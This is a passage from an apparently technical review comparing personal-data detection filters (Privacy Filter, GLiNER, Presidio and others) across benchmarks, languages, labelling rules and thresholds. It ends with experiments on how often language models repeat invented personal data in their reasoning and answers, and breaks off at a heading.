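On credentials, the gap between the token score of 0.842 and the span score of 0.617 comes from errors in where the model starts or ends a span. If a password takes ten tokens and the model marks nine, it finds 90% of the tokens but misses the span. If it marks all ten and the quotation mark next to them, the span still counts as missed, but none of the password leaks. The model card doesn't separate these two cases, so the span score can't show how many credentials would have stayed partly visible.

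### Clues before and after the value

To measure how much the model relies on context, the researchers had language models write three kinds of short English text, with about 1,200 examples of each. In the first kind, a clue came before the value, as in "This is my home landline number" followed by the digits. In the second, the clue came after the value, and in the third, the value appeared alone.

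| Category | Recall, clue before | Recall, clue after | Recall, no clue |
|---|---|---|---|
| Email | 1.000 | 0.974 | 0.962 |
| Person | 0.994 | 0.955 | 0.885 |
| Account number | 1.000 | 0.916 | 0.797 |
| Web address | 0.942 | 0.872 | 0.835 |
| Phone | 0.919 | 0.574 | 0.318 |
| Date | 0.894 | 0.496 | 0.220 |
| Secret | 0.708 | 0.416 | 0.361 |
| Address | 0.414 | 0.368 | 0.214 |
| All | 0.863 | 0.705 | 0.584 |

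Some of the misses without a clue are reasonable, since a bare date may not be anyone's birthday. The middle column is more worrying because the model reads in both directions, yet it misses far more phone numbers and dates when the clue comes second than when it comes first. It may still depend on earlier text, like the generative model it came from, though the researchers don't test this. It detected addresses poorly even when the clue came first.

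This dependence on later words is a problem for a chatbot. If the filter releases a phone number before the next words arrive, it works with less context than the model had in these tests.

The model is particularly prone to missing personal data when the clue that identifies it is far away. In one test, a user says that "marigold" will stand for an electricity account number, then gives the number only after a long stretch of unrelated conversation. Recall fell as the distance grew. de Bourcy and colleagues suspect that the training data contained too few such cases. The model's design probably contributes too. If each of its eight layers passes information across at most 128 tokens, as the card's description implies, a clue can't influence a token more than 1,024 tokens away, however long a text the model accepts.

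Some unusual formats caused the model to miss real values, and others caused it to mistake ordinary words for names. Across nine alternative ways of writing a value, recall ranged from 0.63 to 0.98 and precision from 0.27 to 0.95.

### Results by language

On PII-Masking-300k, F1 varied little between languages, from 0.914 for Dutch to 0.934 for English. The researchers also generated texts in 13 languages that were rare or absent in their synthetic training data. On these texts, F1 was 0.933 for Portuguese, 0.895 for Russian and 0.878 for Arabic, and lowest for Hausa at 0.758.

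The model did worse on short texts with a clue before the value. Recall in the 11 languages other than English ranged from 0.715 for Turkish to 0.821 for Korean. The size of the gap with English is uncertain because the card lists two different recall figures for English without explanation, 0.956 here and 0.863 in the clue test above, apparently for the same 1,181 examples.

Uppala (2026), in *OpenAI Privacy Filter*, found much lower scores in an independent test of the model on MultiCoNER, a collection of encyclopedia-style sentences, counting only people's names. F1 was 0.397 for English, 0.07 for Portuguese, 0.038 for Persian and 0.027 for Ukrainian. Many people in such sentences are presumably public figures, whom Privacy Filter is supposed to leave alone, so these scores don't prove that it would miss a customer's name. But this applies to English too, so it doesn't explain why scores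 in the other languages were so much lower. Uppala also ruled out tokenization as a general explanation, since Hindi words split into more tokens than Persian words, yet Hindi scored 0.268. The most plausible remaining cause is uneven training data. On invented customer-support messages, the model did about as well in French, German and Spanish as in English, with an F1 between 0.596 and 0.645.

In Uppala's results, the model does best on the types of personal data that rules also detect well. On the English customer-support messages, it scored 0.975 for email addresses and 0.920 for phone numbers, but 0.394 for names and 0.304 for addresses. Exact matching may account for part of the gap, as it did for GLiNER Guard.

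### What the makers do not guarantee

de Bourcy and colleagues describe Privacy Filter as an aid for reducing the amount of personal data in a text. They say that it guarantees neither anonymity nor compliance with the law, and that it can't replace a policy review where the stakes are high. They list it as misuse to assume that a text is safe to release because the filter left it unmasked, or to rely on the default operating point without testing it on one's own texts. For medical, legal, financial, personnel, educational and government records, they recommend keeping a human reviewer.

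They also expect more misses for uncommon names, initials and regional naming conventions. People whose names are rare in the training data are therefore more likely to have them left in the output, and average recall doesn't show this difference.

Models also sometimes mask too much. In the sample email that OpenAI published with the release, the masked version hides a product's launch date along with the names and contact details, though the date doesn't identify a private person.

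Users can't add or redefine a category when they run the model. They have to fine-tune it on their own labelled examples. On SPY, the set of legal and medical texts on which Minko and colleagues also tested Presidio, Privacy Filter's token F1 rose from 0.545 to 0.879 after training on 1% of the training texts, and to 0.962 after training on 10%. Some of that gain comes from learning the labelling rules specific to that dataset, so a company should expect a similar gain only if its own labels are consistent.

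An older multilingual model, XLM-RoBERTa, also scored higher than Privacy Filter after fine-tuning on only 500 examples. In Uppala's test on AI4Privacy, another set of invented texts, it reached an F1 of 0.888, against 0.855 for Privacy Filter without fine-tuning. The comparison may favor XLM-RoBERTa, because Uppala describes a more lenient matching rule for it.

### Matching spans to category names

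A travel agency may want to mask booking references, which aren't among Privacy Filter's categories. With a model from the GLiNER family, it can enter "booking reference" as a category and run the detector straight away. *GLiNER* (Zaratiana, Tomeh and colleagues, 2023) introduced the method for general named-entity recognition, and others later adapted it to personal data. GLiNER Guard, the hybrid of rules and a model described earlier, belongs to this family.

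The detector puts the category names in front of the text and processes everything together. It turns each category name into a list of numbers, q, and each stretch of up to 12 words into another list of the same length, S, which it computes from the first and last word. The score for a span and a category is

```
score = σ(S · q)
```

where S · q multiplies the two lists item by item and adds up the results, and σ converts the sum into a value between 0 and 1. Training raises the score for correct pairs and lowers it for all others.

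"Marta Lindqvist called on Tuesday" has five words and therefore 15 possible spans. With the categories "person" and "phone number", the model computes 30 scores. Suppose it gives "Marta Lindqvist" 0.94, "Lindqvist" 0.71 and "Marta" 0.66 for "person", and everything else scores below the usual threshold of 0.5. The detector accepts the highest-scoring span first and discards any that overlap it, so it returns the full name. It needs no begin and end tags because it scores whole spans. Limiting spans to 12 words keeps their number manageable, but a long postal address can exceed that limit.

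Zaratiana and colleagues trained the model on about 45,000 passages in which ChatGPT had labeled 13,000 types of entities, so that it could recognize types that weren't in its training data. On seven test sets from other fields, such as music and politics, the largest version averaged an F1 of 60.9 out of 100, compared with 47.5 for ChatGPT at the time. The English version scored only 0.89 on Bengali, while a multilingual version scored 25.9.

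*GLiNER2* (Zaratiana, Pasternak and colleagues, 2025) lets users add a description to each category name, which helps when a short name is ambiguous. The model has 205 million parameters and runs on an ordinary processor. With 20 labels, it took 163 milliseconds to classify a text, compared with 425 for OpenAI's GPT-4o over the internet. These times are for classifying whole texts, and finding spans within a text may take a different amount of time.

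### GLiNER2-PII against Privacy Filter

In *GLiNER2-PII*, Zaratiana, Lewis and Hurn-Maloney (2026) fine-tuned a GLiNER model to detect personal data. It covers 42 categories, including passport numbers, card security codes and recovery codes, and can mark a first name inside a full name. They trained it on only 4,910 texts in seven languages, all written and labelled by a large language model. The researchers compared it with Privacy Filter and three other GLiNER models on 100 legal and 100 medical texts from SPY, counting a detection as correct only if its boundaries and type matched the label exactly.

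| Detector | Recall: legal | Recall: medical | Precision: legal | Precision: medical | F1: legal | F1: medical |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GLiNER2-PII | 0.722 | 0.681 | 0.354 | 0.355 | 0.475 | 0.467 |
| NVIDIA GLiNER PII | 0.431 | 0.431 | 0.374 | 0.341 | 0.401 | 0.381 |
| gliner_multi_pii-v1 | 0.308 | 0.314 | 0.522 | 0.483 | 0.388 | 0.381 |
| Knowledgator GLiNER PII | 0.372 | 0.319 | 0.398 | 0.389 | 0.385 | 0.350 |
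| Privacy Filter | 0.640 | 0.671 | 0.250 | 0.271 | 0.360 | 0.386 |

GLiNER2-PII had the highest F1 and recall, but nearly two-thirds of its findings counted as wrong. The researchers found that it often mistook common nouns, companies and products for people. Every detector in the table has low precision partly because SPY labels only data about the person who wrote the text, so a correctly marked name of someone else counts as a false alarm.

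GLiNER2-PII's lead over Privacy Filter is uncertain. Its recall on medical texts is only slightly higher, at 0.681 against 0.671. Uppala also tested Privacy Filter on SPY, using up to 2,000 texts from each field, and measured an F1 of 0.453 on legal texts and 0.464 on medical ones. Those scores are close to GLiNER2-PII's in its makers' test. Differences in the sample and in how the researchers mapped each model's categories to SPY's may affect the scores as much as the choice of detector.

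An agency can name its own categories, such as "occupation", which could help it detect quasi-identifiers. But none of GLiNER2-PII's 42 trained categories covers occupation or age, and SPY doesn't label either, so these scores don't measure how well that would work.

### Generative models that list identifiers

A general language model can detect personal data without special training. Uppala instructed GPT-4o to return all personal data in a text as a list of exact strings, then searched the text for each string to find its position.

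The search is a weak point because a generative model returns words, not positions. If the model corrects a misspelt name or drops a space from a phone number, the search finds nothing and the identifier stays in the text. If the model returns "58", the search may also find those digits inside a booking number. When a customer and a ferry share a name, the string alone doesn't show which occurrence to mask.

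The table gives F1 on six English test sets. The GLiNER model here is a general one without special training on personal data.

| Test set | Privacy Filter | Presidio | GLiNER | GPT-4o |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AI4Privacy | 0.855 | 0.431 | 0.577 | 0.543 |
| Nemotron-PII | 0.559 | 0.438 | 0.538 | 0.478 |
| Kiji, customer support | 0.596 | 0.430 | 0.349 | 0.420 |
| Gretel, finance | 0.554 | 0.388 | 0.502 | 0.576 |
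| SPY, medical | 0.464 | 0.273 | 0.498 | 0.702 |
| SPY, legal | 0.453 | 0.285 | 0.502 | 0.587 |

GPT-4o came first on the medical, legal and financial texts. On the medical texts, it found 94.9% of the items, compared with 81.8% for Privacy Filter. Uppala attributes GPT-4o's lower scores on the other three sets to boundaries that didn't match exactly, but didn't test this explanation. If it is right, some of the items counted as misses would still have been at least partly masked. GPT-4o dates from 2024 and is far behind current models, so this design could score higher with a newer model.

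### Generative models that rewrite the text

A generative model can also return the whole text with masks in place of the identifiers. *PRvL* (Garza, Kotal and colleagues, 2025) compared three ways of preparing models for this. Fine-tuning trains a model on pairs of original and masked texts. Instruction tuning trains it on explicit instructions with a few worked examples. Retrieval leaves the model unchanged and adds similar masked examples to each prompt. Without any of these, the open models often failed to produce a masked text at all.

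A rewritten text may differ from the original in length and wording, so the researchers couldn't compare it with the labels position by position. Instead, they counted the edits needed to turn the model's version into the correct one, scoring each inserted mask as a miss and each deleted mask as a false alarm. They also measured leakage, the number of personal-data tokens left unmasked divided by all tokens in the output. If a tenth of a text is personal data, a leakage of 0.002 means 2% of that data remained unmasked.

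The table shows results on 1,000 invented English texts from the same source as the training data. BERT-NER, a conventional token classifier, had no reported leakage on this set.

| Model | Preparation | Precision | Recall | Leakage |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| BERT-NER | Token classifier | 0.907 | 0.982 | – |
| DeepSeek-Q1 | Instruction tuning | 0.973 | 0.981 | 0.002 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | Instruction tuning | 0.975 | 0.962 | 0.004 |
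| Mixtral | Fine-tuning | 0.940 | 0.957 | 0.004 |
| GPT-4 | Retrieval | 0.886 | 0.900 | 0.011 |
| Mixtral | Retrieval | 0.803 | 0.776 | 0.028 |

These scores count a mask as correct even if it names the wrong type. The token classifier missed no more personal data than the best generative model, although Garza and colleagues emphasise the strength of instruction tuning. The larger models were better only in precision, as in the tutoring transcripts. They had a clearer advantage in languages absent from their training for this task. On Italian texts, BERT-NER kept a recall of 0.915 but its precision fell to 0.301, while Llama 3.1 kept both above 0.96.

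Every model the researchers tried had lower recall on English texts from an outside collection: 0.737 for BERT-NER, 0.700 for Llama 3.1 and 0.776 for GPT-4. A company whose texts differ from the training set should expect recall closer to these figures. All the results should be treated as approximate because the study gives conflicting values for a few of them, such as a leakage of 0.205 in one table and 0.028 in another for the same model.

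Unlike the other designs, rewriting also risks changing text that contains no personal data. In one example from the study, the model returned "Thank you for your interest" with a mask for a name that wasn't in the original. In the travel agency's answer, the same kind of error could change the number of days given for a refund. To guard against this, the filter can reject any rewrite whose text outside the masks doesn't match the original.

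### Speed and cost

Generating text is slow because the model produces one token at a time. In Garza and colleagues' measurements, 150 tokens, roughly a short email, took 1.5 seconds with DeepSeek-Q1 and 7.9 seconds with GPT-4. Listing the identifiers takes less time than rewriting the full text because the list is usually shorter. Privacy Filter and the GLiNER models score the whole text at once. In the sample run in Privacy Filter's model card, a seven-word sentence took 65 milliseconds on unspecified hardware.

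Training is a smaller obstacle. Garza and colleagues needed about one to 13 hours per model on two graphics cards. A company can avoid training by using a hosted model, but if the host is a new party, the company sends it the data that the filter is meant to protect.

### The designs on the same documents

*RedactionBench* (Brynjólfsson, Jayakrishnan and colleagues, 2026) tested 35 models on 200 documents of up to ten pages, about half of them based on real documents. It separates items that a filter must always mask, such as access keys, from items that depend on the context. A model's score is the number of mandatory items it covered, divided by the sum of all mandatory items and penalties for false alarms. For example, a model that covers eight of ten mandatory items and raises two ordinary false alarms scores 8/12, or 0.67. Masking or leaving a context-dependent item doesn't affect the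 score unless the model masks only part of it.

| Design | Best score |
|---|---|
| Token classifiers, including Privacy Filter | 0.58 |
| GLiNER models | 0.47 |
| Small generative models trained for extraction or masking | 0.45 |

The largest general models, which edited the documents with software tools, averaged 0.71. The researchers derived the spans from these edits instead of searching for strings the models returned. Among models small enough to run locally, the token classifiers did best. The small generative models lost the advantage they had shown in *PRvL* on texts similar to their training data.

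On a subset of 48 documents, the large models averaged 0.81 and human volunteers averaged 0.77. The volunteers agreed with the researchers on 89.4% of the mandatory items and 94.1% of the text that should stay, but on only 47.7% of the items that depend on context. A detector's score on those context-dependent items would depend heavily on who labeled them.

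## Why test sets give the same detector different scores

Privacy Filter, OpenAI's token classifier, has an F1 of 0.96 on PII-Masking-300k but about 0.5 on several other test sets. Two further studies widen the range. *REDACT* (Vats, Agrawal and colleagues, 2026) tested Privacy Filter on invented texts in 25 languages. *Surprise Masking* (Tyagi, Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, 2026) tested it on about 100,000 texts from PIIBench, the merged collection on which Presidio did badly.

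| Test set | Tested by | Unit of scoring | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| PII-Masking-300k | de Bourcy and colleagues | Token | 0.960 |
| PII-Masking-300k | de Bourcy and colleagues | Exact span | 0.926 |
| PII-Masking-300k | Uppala | Exact span | 0.855 |
| SPY, legal and medical | de Bourcy and colleagues | Token | 0.545 |
| SPY, medical | Uppala | Exact span | 0.464 |
| SPY, medical | Zaratiana and colleagues | Exact span | 0.386 |
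| REDACT | Vats and colleagues | Overlapping span | 0.512 |
| REDACT | Vats and colleagues | Exact span | 0.171 |
| PIIBench | Tyagi and colleagues | Character | 0.325 |

*Locale-Conditioned Few-Shot Prompting Mitigates Demonstration Regurgitation in On-Device PII Substitution* (2026) reports an F1 of only 0.587, even on 100 synthetic examples bundled with the model's test software.

Preparing the same test set differently can change a detector's score. The two exact-span results on PII-Masking-300k differ by 0.07. Before scoring, de Bourcy and colleagues dropped the categories that Privacy Filter doesn't cover and used rules to clean up conflicting labels. Uppala scored at most 2,000 of the texts. These choices probably explain most of the difference, but the gap between 0.96 and 0.5 has larger causes.

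### SPY and the author's own data

In *SPY*, Savkin, Ionov and Konovalov (2025) wanted to test whether a detector can tell personal data from other names and numbers. They had the language model Llama-3-70B write legal questions and medical consultations, then add placeholders for the name, phone number and other details of each text's fictional author. A program filled these with invented values. Llama then added details unrelated to the author, such as a legal team's website. The researchers labelled only the author's details as personal data.

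A detector that marks every name does badly under this rule. In the legal questions, Presidio found 79.4% of the labelled names, but only 17.9% of the names it marked were correct.

The rule makes sense for a forum that wants to protect whoever is posting, but not for the travel agency. The assistant wrote the answer about Marta Lindqvist, so by SPY's definition the answer contains no personal data, and masking her passport number would count as a false alarm.

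In de Bourcy and colleagues' test, training Privacy Filter on a tenth of SPY's training texts (at most about 870, since SPY has 8,688 texts in total) raised its F1 from 0.545 to 0.962, mostly because the model learned this rule. Precision rose from 0.414 to 0.963 and recall from 0.795 to 0.960, as the model learned to leave other people's details alone and to recognise SPY's unusual account numbers. Llama wrote both the training and the test texts, so Privacy Filter may also have learned how Llama tends to introduce a phone number. The F1 of 0.962 is therefore weak evidence of how well the tuned model would do on a company's own texts.

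Savkin and colleagues found that the rule carries over from one subject to another. They trained DeBERTa, an older token classifier, on one half of SPY and tested it on the other. For names, its F1 was 0.90 on the legal questions and 0.88 on the medical ones. Uppala's XLM-RoBERTa, however, reached only 0.477 after training on 3,592 medical texts. Two other models learned the task from similar or smaller amounts of data, so the low score probably reflects a problem in that experiment.

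### REDACT and its 51 types

Test sets also differ in how many types of data they include. Vats and colleagues labelled 51, from passport numbers to religion and job titles. They varied nine properties of the text, including language, subject, format and length. Covering every combination would have taken 10.9 million texts, so they planned a much smaller set in which every pair of values, such as Hindi and a chat transcript, occurs at least once. The finished set has 13,427 texts, all written by a language model, with an average of 24 labelled items each. The researchers ran five detectors on 1,000 of these texts, using 40 from each language.

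| Detector | F1, overlapping spans | F1, all types weighted equally | Recall, high-sensitivity items |
|---|---|---|---|
| Presidio | 0.195 | 0.063 | 0.07 |
| GLiNER | 0.320 | 0.224 | 0.42 |
| Privacy Filter | 0.512 | 0.254 | 0.57 |
| GPT-4.1 | 0.597 | 0.565 | 0.74 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0.636 | 0.619 | 0.77 |

Privacy Filter's score halves when all 51 types of personal data count equally, because it has only eight categories and none covers religion or job titles. The general language models' scores drop only slightly, since their instructions can list any type.

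High-sensitivity items include religion, health, criminal offences and dates of birth. Names, phone numbers and passport numbers are medium-sensitivity, and quasi-identifiers such as towns and job titles are low. Presidio's recall was 0.23 on the low group and 0.07 on the high one, while the other four detectors did best on the high group. Vats and colleagues caution that invented texts may state a religion or an illness more plainly than real ones do. They also note that Privacy Filter's 0.57 comes largely from its broad categories for numbers and accounts, and that it still detects religion poorly. The groupings are also uncertain, because two annotators who checked a sample agreed on the sensitivity group for 90.5% of items, but their kappa, which measures agreement beyond chance, was only 0.25.

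The researchers also recorded how fully each item appears in the text. Presidio found 23% of complete items but only 2% of partial ones, such as "J. Smith" or the last four digits of an account number. GPT-4.1 found 78% of the partial items and Claude Sonnet 4.6 found 84%. Partial items matter for filtering because initials and last digits can still identify someone. Recall on another group, obfuscated items, is harder to interpret because the group includes masks such as "[NAME]", which expose nobody if a filter leaves them in place.

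### Cisco's relabelling study

Two test sets can use the same name for a type but include different things in it. In *Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels* (2026), Hsu and Berlin of Cisco measured the effect by relabelling two public test sets. They wrote a definition for each of 12 types, stating what the type covers, what evidence the text must contain, where a span starts and ends, and how to treat difficult cases. For example, a 16-digit number that the text calls an order number isn't a card number, even if it has the right format, but a number that the text presents as a card number counts even if it fails the Luhn checksum. They then used OpenAI's GPT-5 Mini to apply the definitions to every text.

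The two sets of labels disagreed most about card, driving licence, passport, social security and tax numbers in the AI4Privacy set, a later collection from the makers of PII-Masking-300k. For each type, 59% to 86% of the texts marked as containing it in at least one set of labels were marked only in the original set. For example, only the original labels mark "Don't forget to bring your YV9022888!" as containing a passport number.

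Hsu and Berlin searched the texts for words that name the type of personal data, such as "passport". These words appeared in 54.2% of the texts that both sets of labels counted, but in only 0.24% of those that the new labels dropped. Looser clues such as "ID" or "payment" appeared in 80.4% of the first group and 27.5% of the second.

Whether YV9022888 should count depends on what the filter is for. Someone who steals a real passport number can use it even without the word "passport" next to it, and in a chat that word may be in an earlier message. But a filter that masks every code in this format will also mask booking references.

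To check the new labels, Hsu and Berlin asked two other language models to judge 50 disagreements for each of the five types. GPT-5.6-Sol agreed with the new labels in 68% of cases and Claude Opus 5 in 72%. The researchers then read only the cases where both models preferred the original label. Most were inconclusive or relied on a national format, such as 756.0754.6599.08, which has the form of a Swiss social security number. Hsu and Berlin accept that their definitions should treat such formats as sufficient evidence. The audit supports most of the removals but leaves a substantial share in doubt.

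In the other test set, Nemotron-PII, the new labels mainly added items. Of the texts counted as containing an IP address, 29% were counted only under the new labels, nearly always because the address was inside a URL. The judges agreed with 100% and 98% of the additions they checked.

### One detector, two sets of labels

Hsu and Berlin also built a detector, which they trained on 1.12 million relabelled texts from 77 public datasets. It has 141 million parameters and two classifiers that share most of their computation. One predicts which types of personal data occur anywhere in the text, and the other scores each token for each type. The detector keeps a span only if the whole-text classifier also flags its type. The token classifier can therefore use a low threshold to find more spans, without the detector marking every number that resembles personal data.

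The researchers set the thresholds using 100,000 real conversations from WildChat, a collection of chats that users agreed to share for research. For each detector and type, they chose the lowest threshold at which the detector falsely flagged no more than 0.1% of conversations. The table gives recall at those thresholds, first under the new labels and then under the original ones. Each detector's output is the same for both figures.

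| Type and test set | Cisco's detector | NVIDIA GLiNER PII | GLiNER2-PII |
|---|---|---|---|
| Passport number, AI4Privacy | 0.967 / 0.740 | – | 0.825 / 0.197 |
| Social security number, AI4Privacy | 0.923 / 0.237 | 0.494 / 0.126 | – |
| Card number, AI4Privacy | 0.976 / 0.955 | 0.685 / 0.573 | 0.568 / 0.416 |
| Phone number, AI4Privacy | 0.904 / 0.797 | 0.808 / 0.743 | 0.935 / 0.886 |
| IP address, Nemotron-PII | 0.986 / 0.999 | 0.721 / 0.995 | 0.652 / 0.922 |

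Changing only the labels shifts the recall of Cisco's detector on social security numbers by 69 percentage points and lowers NVIDIA's score on IP addresses from nearly perfect to mediocre. NVIDIA trained its model on the Nemotron-PII training texts, where IP addresses inside URLs are not labeled, so the model probably learned to ignore them.

Cisco's detector had the highest recall in 11 of 14 comparisons under the new labels. Those labels favour it, because Hsu and Berlin trained it on labels of the same kind and used them to decide which WildChat flags were false. Its lead in 9 of 14 comparisons under the original labels is stronger evidence. Privacy Filter could be compared only on email addresses and phone numbers, and it scored highest on AI4Privacy's phone numbers, with 0.948 and 0.953.

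The choice of personal data types affects the score as much as the labels do. On Nemotron-PII, Uppala measured an exact-span F1 of 0.559 for Privacy Filter across all types. Hsu and Berlin measured 0.922 for email addresses and phone numbers alone, with their own labels and tuned thresholds.

### Invented texts and real medical notes

All the test sets in the opening table consist wholly or partly of invented texts. *MedDeID enables locally governed clinical-text de-identification from real or synthetic training data* (Hellemans, Stroobants and colleagues, 2026) reports tests of detectors on real Dutch medical notes. Privacy Filter found 72.1% of the identifying text in 300 hospital notes. In family doctors' notes, it masked 11.46% of the non-identifying text, compared with 0.29% for a model that the researchers had trained on hospital notes.

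Privacy Filter's recall on the invented Dutch texts in PII-Masking-300k was 0.937, so the Dutch language alone doesn't explain the misses. Real notes have their own shorthand and layout. The annotators also marked ages, which Privacy Filter has no category for, so part of the gap again comes from different definitions of personal data.

A second model gives a cleaner comparison because the researchers used the same labelling scheme throughout. They trained it only on invented Dutch notes.

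| Test notes | Model trained on invented notes | Model trained on hospital notes |
|---|---|---|
| Invented | 99.8% | 96.6% |
| Hospital | 96.1% | 98.9% |
| Family doctors | 90.3% | 87.0% |

The model trained on invented notes missed 0.2% of the identifying text in invented notes, 3.9% in the hospital notes and 9.7% in the family doctors' notes. Training on real notes didn't solve the problem either. The hospital-trained model's score fell by almost 12 percentage points from the hospital notes to the family doctors' notes, where it did worse than the model trained only on invented notes.

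### Language and subject

Uppala tested Privacy Filter on 32 datasets in 14 languages, covering personal data, customer support, finance, medicine, law and general named-entity recognition. Its F1 ranged from 0.534 in Danish to 0.645 in Spanish on the customer-support messages, and from 0.453 to 0.855 on the six English personal-data sets. Among Latin-alphabet languages, the subject and the labels therefore affected the score more than the language did.

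Other scripts may be a larger problem. Privacy Filter scored very low on Persian and Ukrainian names, but the test used encyclopedia-style sentences, so these scores are a poor guide to its performance on customer data. Hsu and Berlin provide a better comparison, using only card, social security and tax numbers included in both sets of labels. Their detector found at least 96.9% of these in each of six European languages, but only 65.3% in Hindi and 65.4% in Telugu. NVIDIA's model found 41.1% in Hindi and 50.6% in Telugu. The values are mostly digits, so the words around them probably cause the difficulty.

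A detector can also get similar F1 scores on two test sets but have opposite weaknesses. Uppala tested Privacy Filter on English customer-support messages and financial documents. In the messages, it found 84% of the items, but more than half of its findings were wrong. In the financial documents, 64% of its findings were correct, but it missed half the items. According to Uppala, it recognised formatted account numbers in the financial documents but missed details in running text, such as employers' names.

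### Matching rules and thresholds

The matching rule can change how detectors rank. When Vats and colleagues required exact spans, Claude Sonnet 4.6 fell only from 0.636 to 0.602, but Privacy Filter fell from 0.512 to 0.171, below GLiNER's 0.293. This may be partly because REDACT labels the first name and surname separately as well as the full name.

A detector's score also depends on its operating point, so a gap between a tuned detector and an untuned one may come from the tuning. As released, Privacy Filter had an F1 of 0.325 on PIIBench. Tyagi and colleagues then replaced its usual decoding with a threshold on how much more likely a personal-data label was than the background label. They chose the threshold using 10,000 other PIIBench texts, and F1 rose to 0.513 without any retraining. A DeBERTa model trained for the task reached 0.785.

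Some tests count whole documents. Walia, Nudell and Chohlas-Wood (2026), in *Algorithm Validation as a Policy Audit*, tested a system that removes names, mentions of race and descriptions of skin colour from US police reports before prosecutors read them. A report failed if even one mention remained, and 3.3% of the reports failed. This standard is demanding because a detector with a recall of 0.99 and independent misses would leave something behind in 39% of documents with 50 items each.

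### False alarms among a million answers

Even a test with perfect labels can give misleading results if identifiers are more common in it than in real use. Suppose a chatbot writes a million answers, 0.5% of them contain an identifier, and the detector flags 90% of those.

| | False positive rate 0.1% | False positive rate 2% |
|---|---|---|
| Answers with an identifier | 5,000 | 5,000 |
| Correctly flagged | 4,500 | 4,500 |
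| Missed | 500 | 500 |
| Answers without an identifier | 995,000 | 995,000 |
| Wrongly flagged | 995 | 19,900 |
| Precision | 82% | 18% |

At a false positive rate of 2%, a colleague reviewing the flagged answers has to open more than five for each one that contains an identifier. The detector's F1 is 0.31 on the million answers, but it would be 0.94 on a test set in which half the texts contain an identifier.

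The 0.5% figure is plausible for general chat. Under Hsu and Berlin's labels, 0.41% of the WildChat conversations contained a phone number. An assistant that reads customer files would produce identifiers far more often, so its filter would have higher precision.

Hsu and Berlin's limit of 0.1% also applies to each type separately. With 12 types, up to 1.2% of conversations could receive a false flag. At that rate, precision in the example would be about 27%. But stricter thresholds lower recall. Relaxing the limit from 0.1% to 0.5% per type raised GLiNER2-PII's recall on AI4Privacy card numbers from 0.568 to 0.815 under the new labels.

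### Using scores to choose a filter

Published scores are most useful for ruling detectors out. Presidio scored below Privacy Filter on all six of Uppala's English test sets for personal data and on REDACT, so a company that needs to find names in ordinary prose has good reason not to rely on Presidio's default settings. Small differences between the leading detectors mean little, because a different matching rule or set of labels can reverse them.

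Scores for individual types of personal data are more informative than an overall F1. The travel agency would need recall on passport and phone numbers, from a test that counts details about customers mentioned by someone else as personal data. It would also need the false positive rate at the same threshold, measured on texts, most of which contain no identifiers. Few published tests provide both.

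The agency can measure the rest on its own answers, once it has written down what the filter should remove. If 0.5% of answers contain an identifier, a random sample of 10,000 would include about 50 such answers. That is enough to estimate a recall of 0.90 to within about eight percentage points, so the agency could tell a good detector from a poor one, but not a recall of 0.90 from one of 0.95. With the same sample, it could easily tell a false positive rate of 0.1% (about 10 false alarms) from one of 2% (about 200).

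## Experiments with filters placed behind a language model

The tests described so far ran detectors on stored texts. A filter behind a chatbot processes newly generated text, which depends on how the user asks and how long the model reasons. In *Safer Reasoning Traces*, Ahrend, Eder and colleagues (2026) gave invented personal data to six language models, counted how often the models repeated it, and ran five filters on the responses.

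### How often the models repeated personal data

In each run, Ahrend and colleagues first gave the model one item of personal data, such as an email address, as part of a fictional study. They then asked for it back using one of two prompts. The plain prompt only asked the question, while the other also told the model to think step by step, explain its reasoning, and return the steps and the final answer in a fixed format. They assumed an assistant that isn't supposed to repeat personal data, so they counted a leak whenever the item appeared in the reasoning or the answer. The whole item had to match, apart from capitalization and spaces.

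They used 11 types of data in three risk groups. With 100 runs for each type, model and prompt, this made 13,200 runs.

| Risk group | Types | Weight in scoring | Leakage, step-by-step prompt |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mild | Name, sex, job title, company | 1 | 98.3% |
| Medium | Date of birth, phone number, email address, IP address, MAC address (a device's hardware number) | 3 | 89.3% |
| High | Card number, social security number | 9 | 55.0% |

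Average leakage rose from 52.3% with the plain prompt to 86.3% with the step-by-step one.

| Model | Plain prompt | Step-by-step prompt |
|---|---|---|
| Mixtral 8×22B | 92.5% | 99.5% |
| Qwen3 32B | 64.8% | 93.6% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 56.5% | 99.1% |
| Claude Opus | 45.8% | 85.0% |
| DeepSeek-R1 70B | 37.5% | 77.0% |
| OpenAI o3 | 16.8% | 63.7% |

Llama repeated the social security number in 4 of 100 plain runs and in all 100 step-by-step runs. Claude Opus never repeated a card number, but it repeated social security numbers in 51 step-by-step runs, up from 0 plain runs. The safety flag that Anthropic returns with Claude's responses wasn't triggered in any of 100 trials.

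Unlike the other prompt, the step-by-step prompt asks for reasoning, reminds the model that it has the item, and asks for the final answer in a separate field. To come closer to isolating the effect of reasoning, the researchers ran a further experiment on six of the types, limiting five of the models to between 0 and 1,035 reasoning tokens. Average leakage was 38.9% without reasoning, 57.3% with 138 tokens and 67.3% with 1,035.

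Four of the models leaked more as soon as they were allowed any reasoning, and extra tokens changed little after that. The leak rate for OpenAI's o3 rose more gradually, from 0% at 138 tokens to 56.7% at 1,035. Low limits often cut its responses short, so some of its low rates come from unfinished answers. The wording of the request seems to matter too. Llama leaked the same six types in 98% of step-by-step runs in the main experiment, but in only 47% of runs at every limit above zero here.

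These leaks matter when someone other than the user reads the text, such as an engineer who opens the log. For models that act as personal assistants, *Leaky Thoughts* (Green, Gubri and colleagues, 2025) disputes developers' common assumption that a model's reasoning stays internal and is therefore safe. *Chain-of-Sanitized-Thoughts* notes that the reasoning can expose personal data even when the final answer does not, and proposes training models to reason without such data. A company that relies on a filter instead has to run it on both the reasoning and the answer.

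### Five filters on the same responses

Ahrend and colleagues then tested the filters on the step-by-step responses, which contained 5,697 leaks. Each filter gave a single yes or no for each response, so the results apply to blocking responses rather than masking single words.

The rules covered seven of the 11 types, leaving out names, sex, job titles and companies. Some were crude. The rule for social security numbers checked for a hyphen, and the one for phone numbers checked for a plus sign.

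The word-statistics classifier weighted each word and word pair according to how common it was, then used the weights to estimate whether the response contained personal data. The researchers trained it on 2,220 texts with and without personal data. GLiNER2, which matches stretches of text to category names, needed no training for the task.

The last two filters were judges, language models that read the response and reported whether it contained a leak. They were OpenAI's small o4-mini and Claude Opus. In early versions, the judge sometimes repeated its instructions and wrote long replies, which could themselves have leaked data. The final prompts prohibited quoting and set a fixed format for the verdict.

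### The formulas and the two recalls

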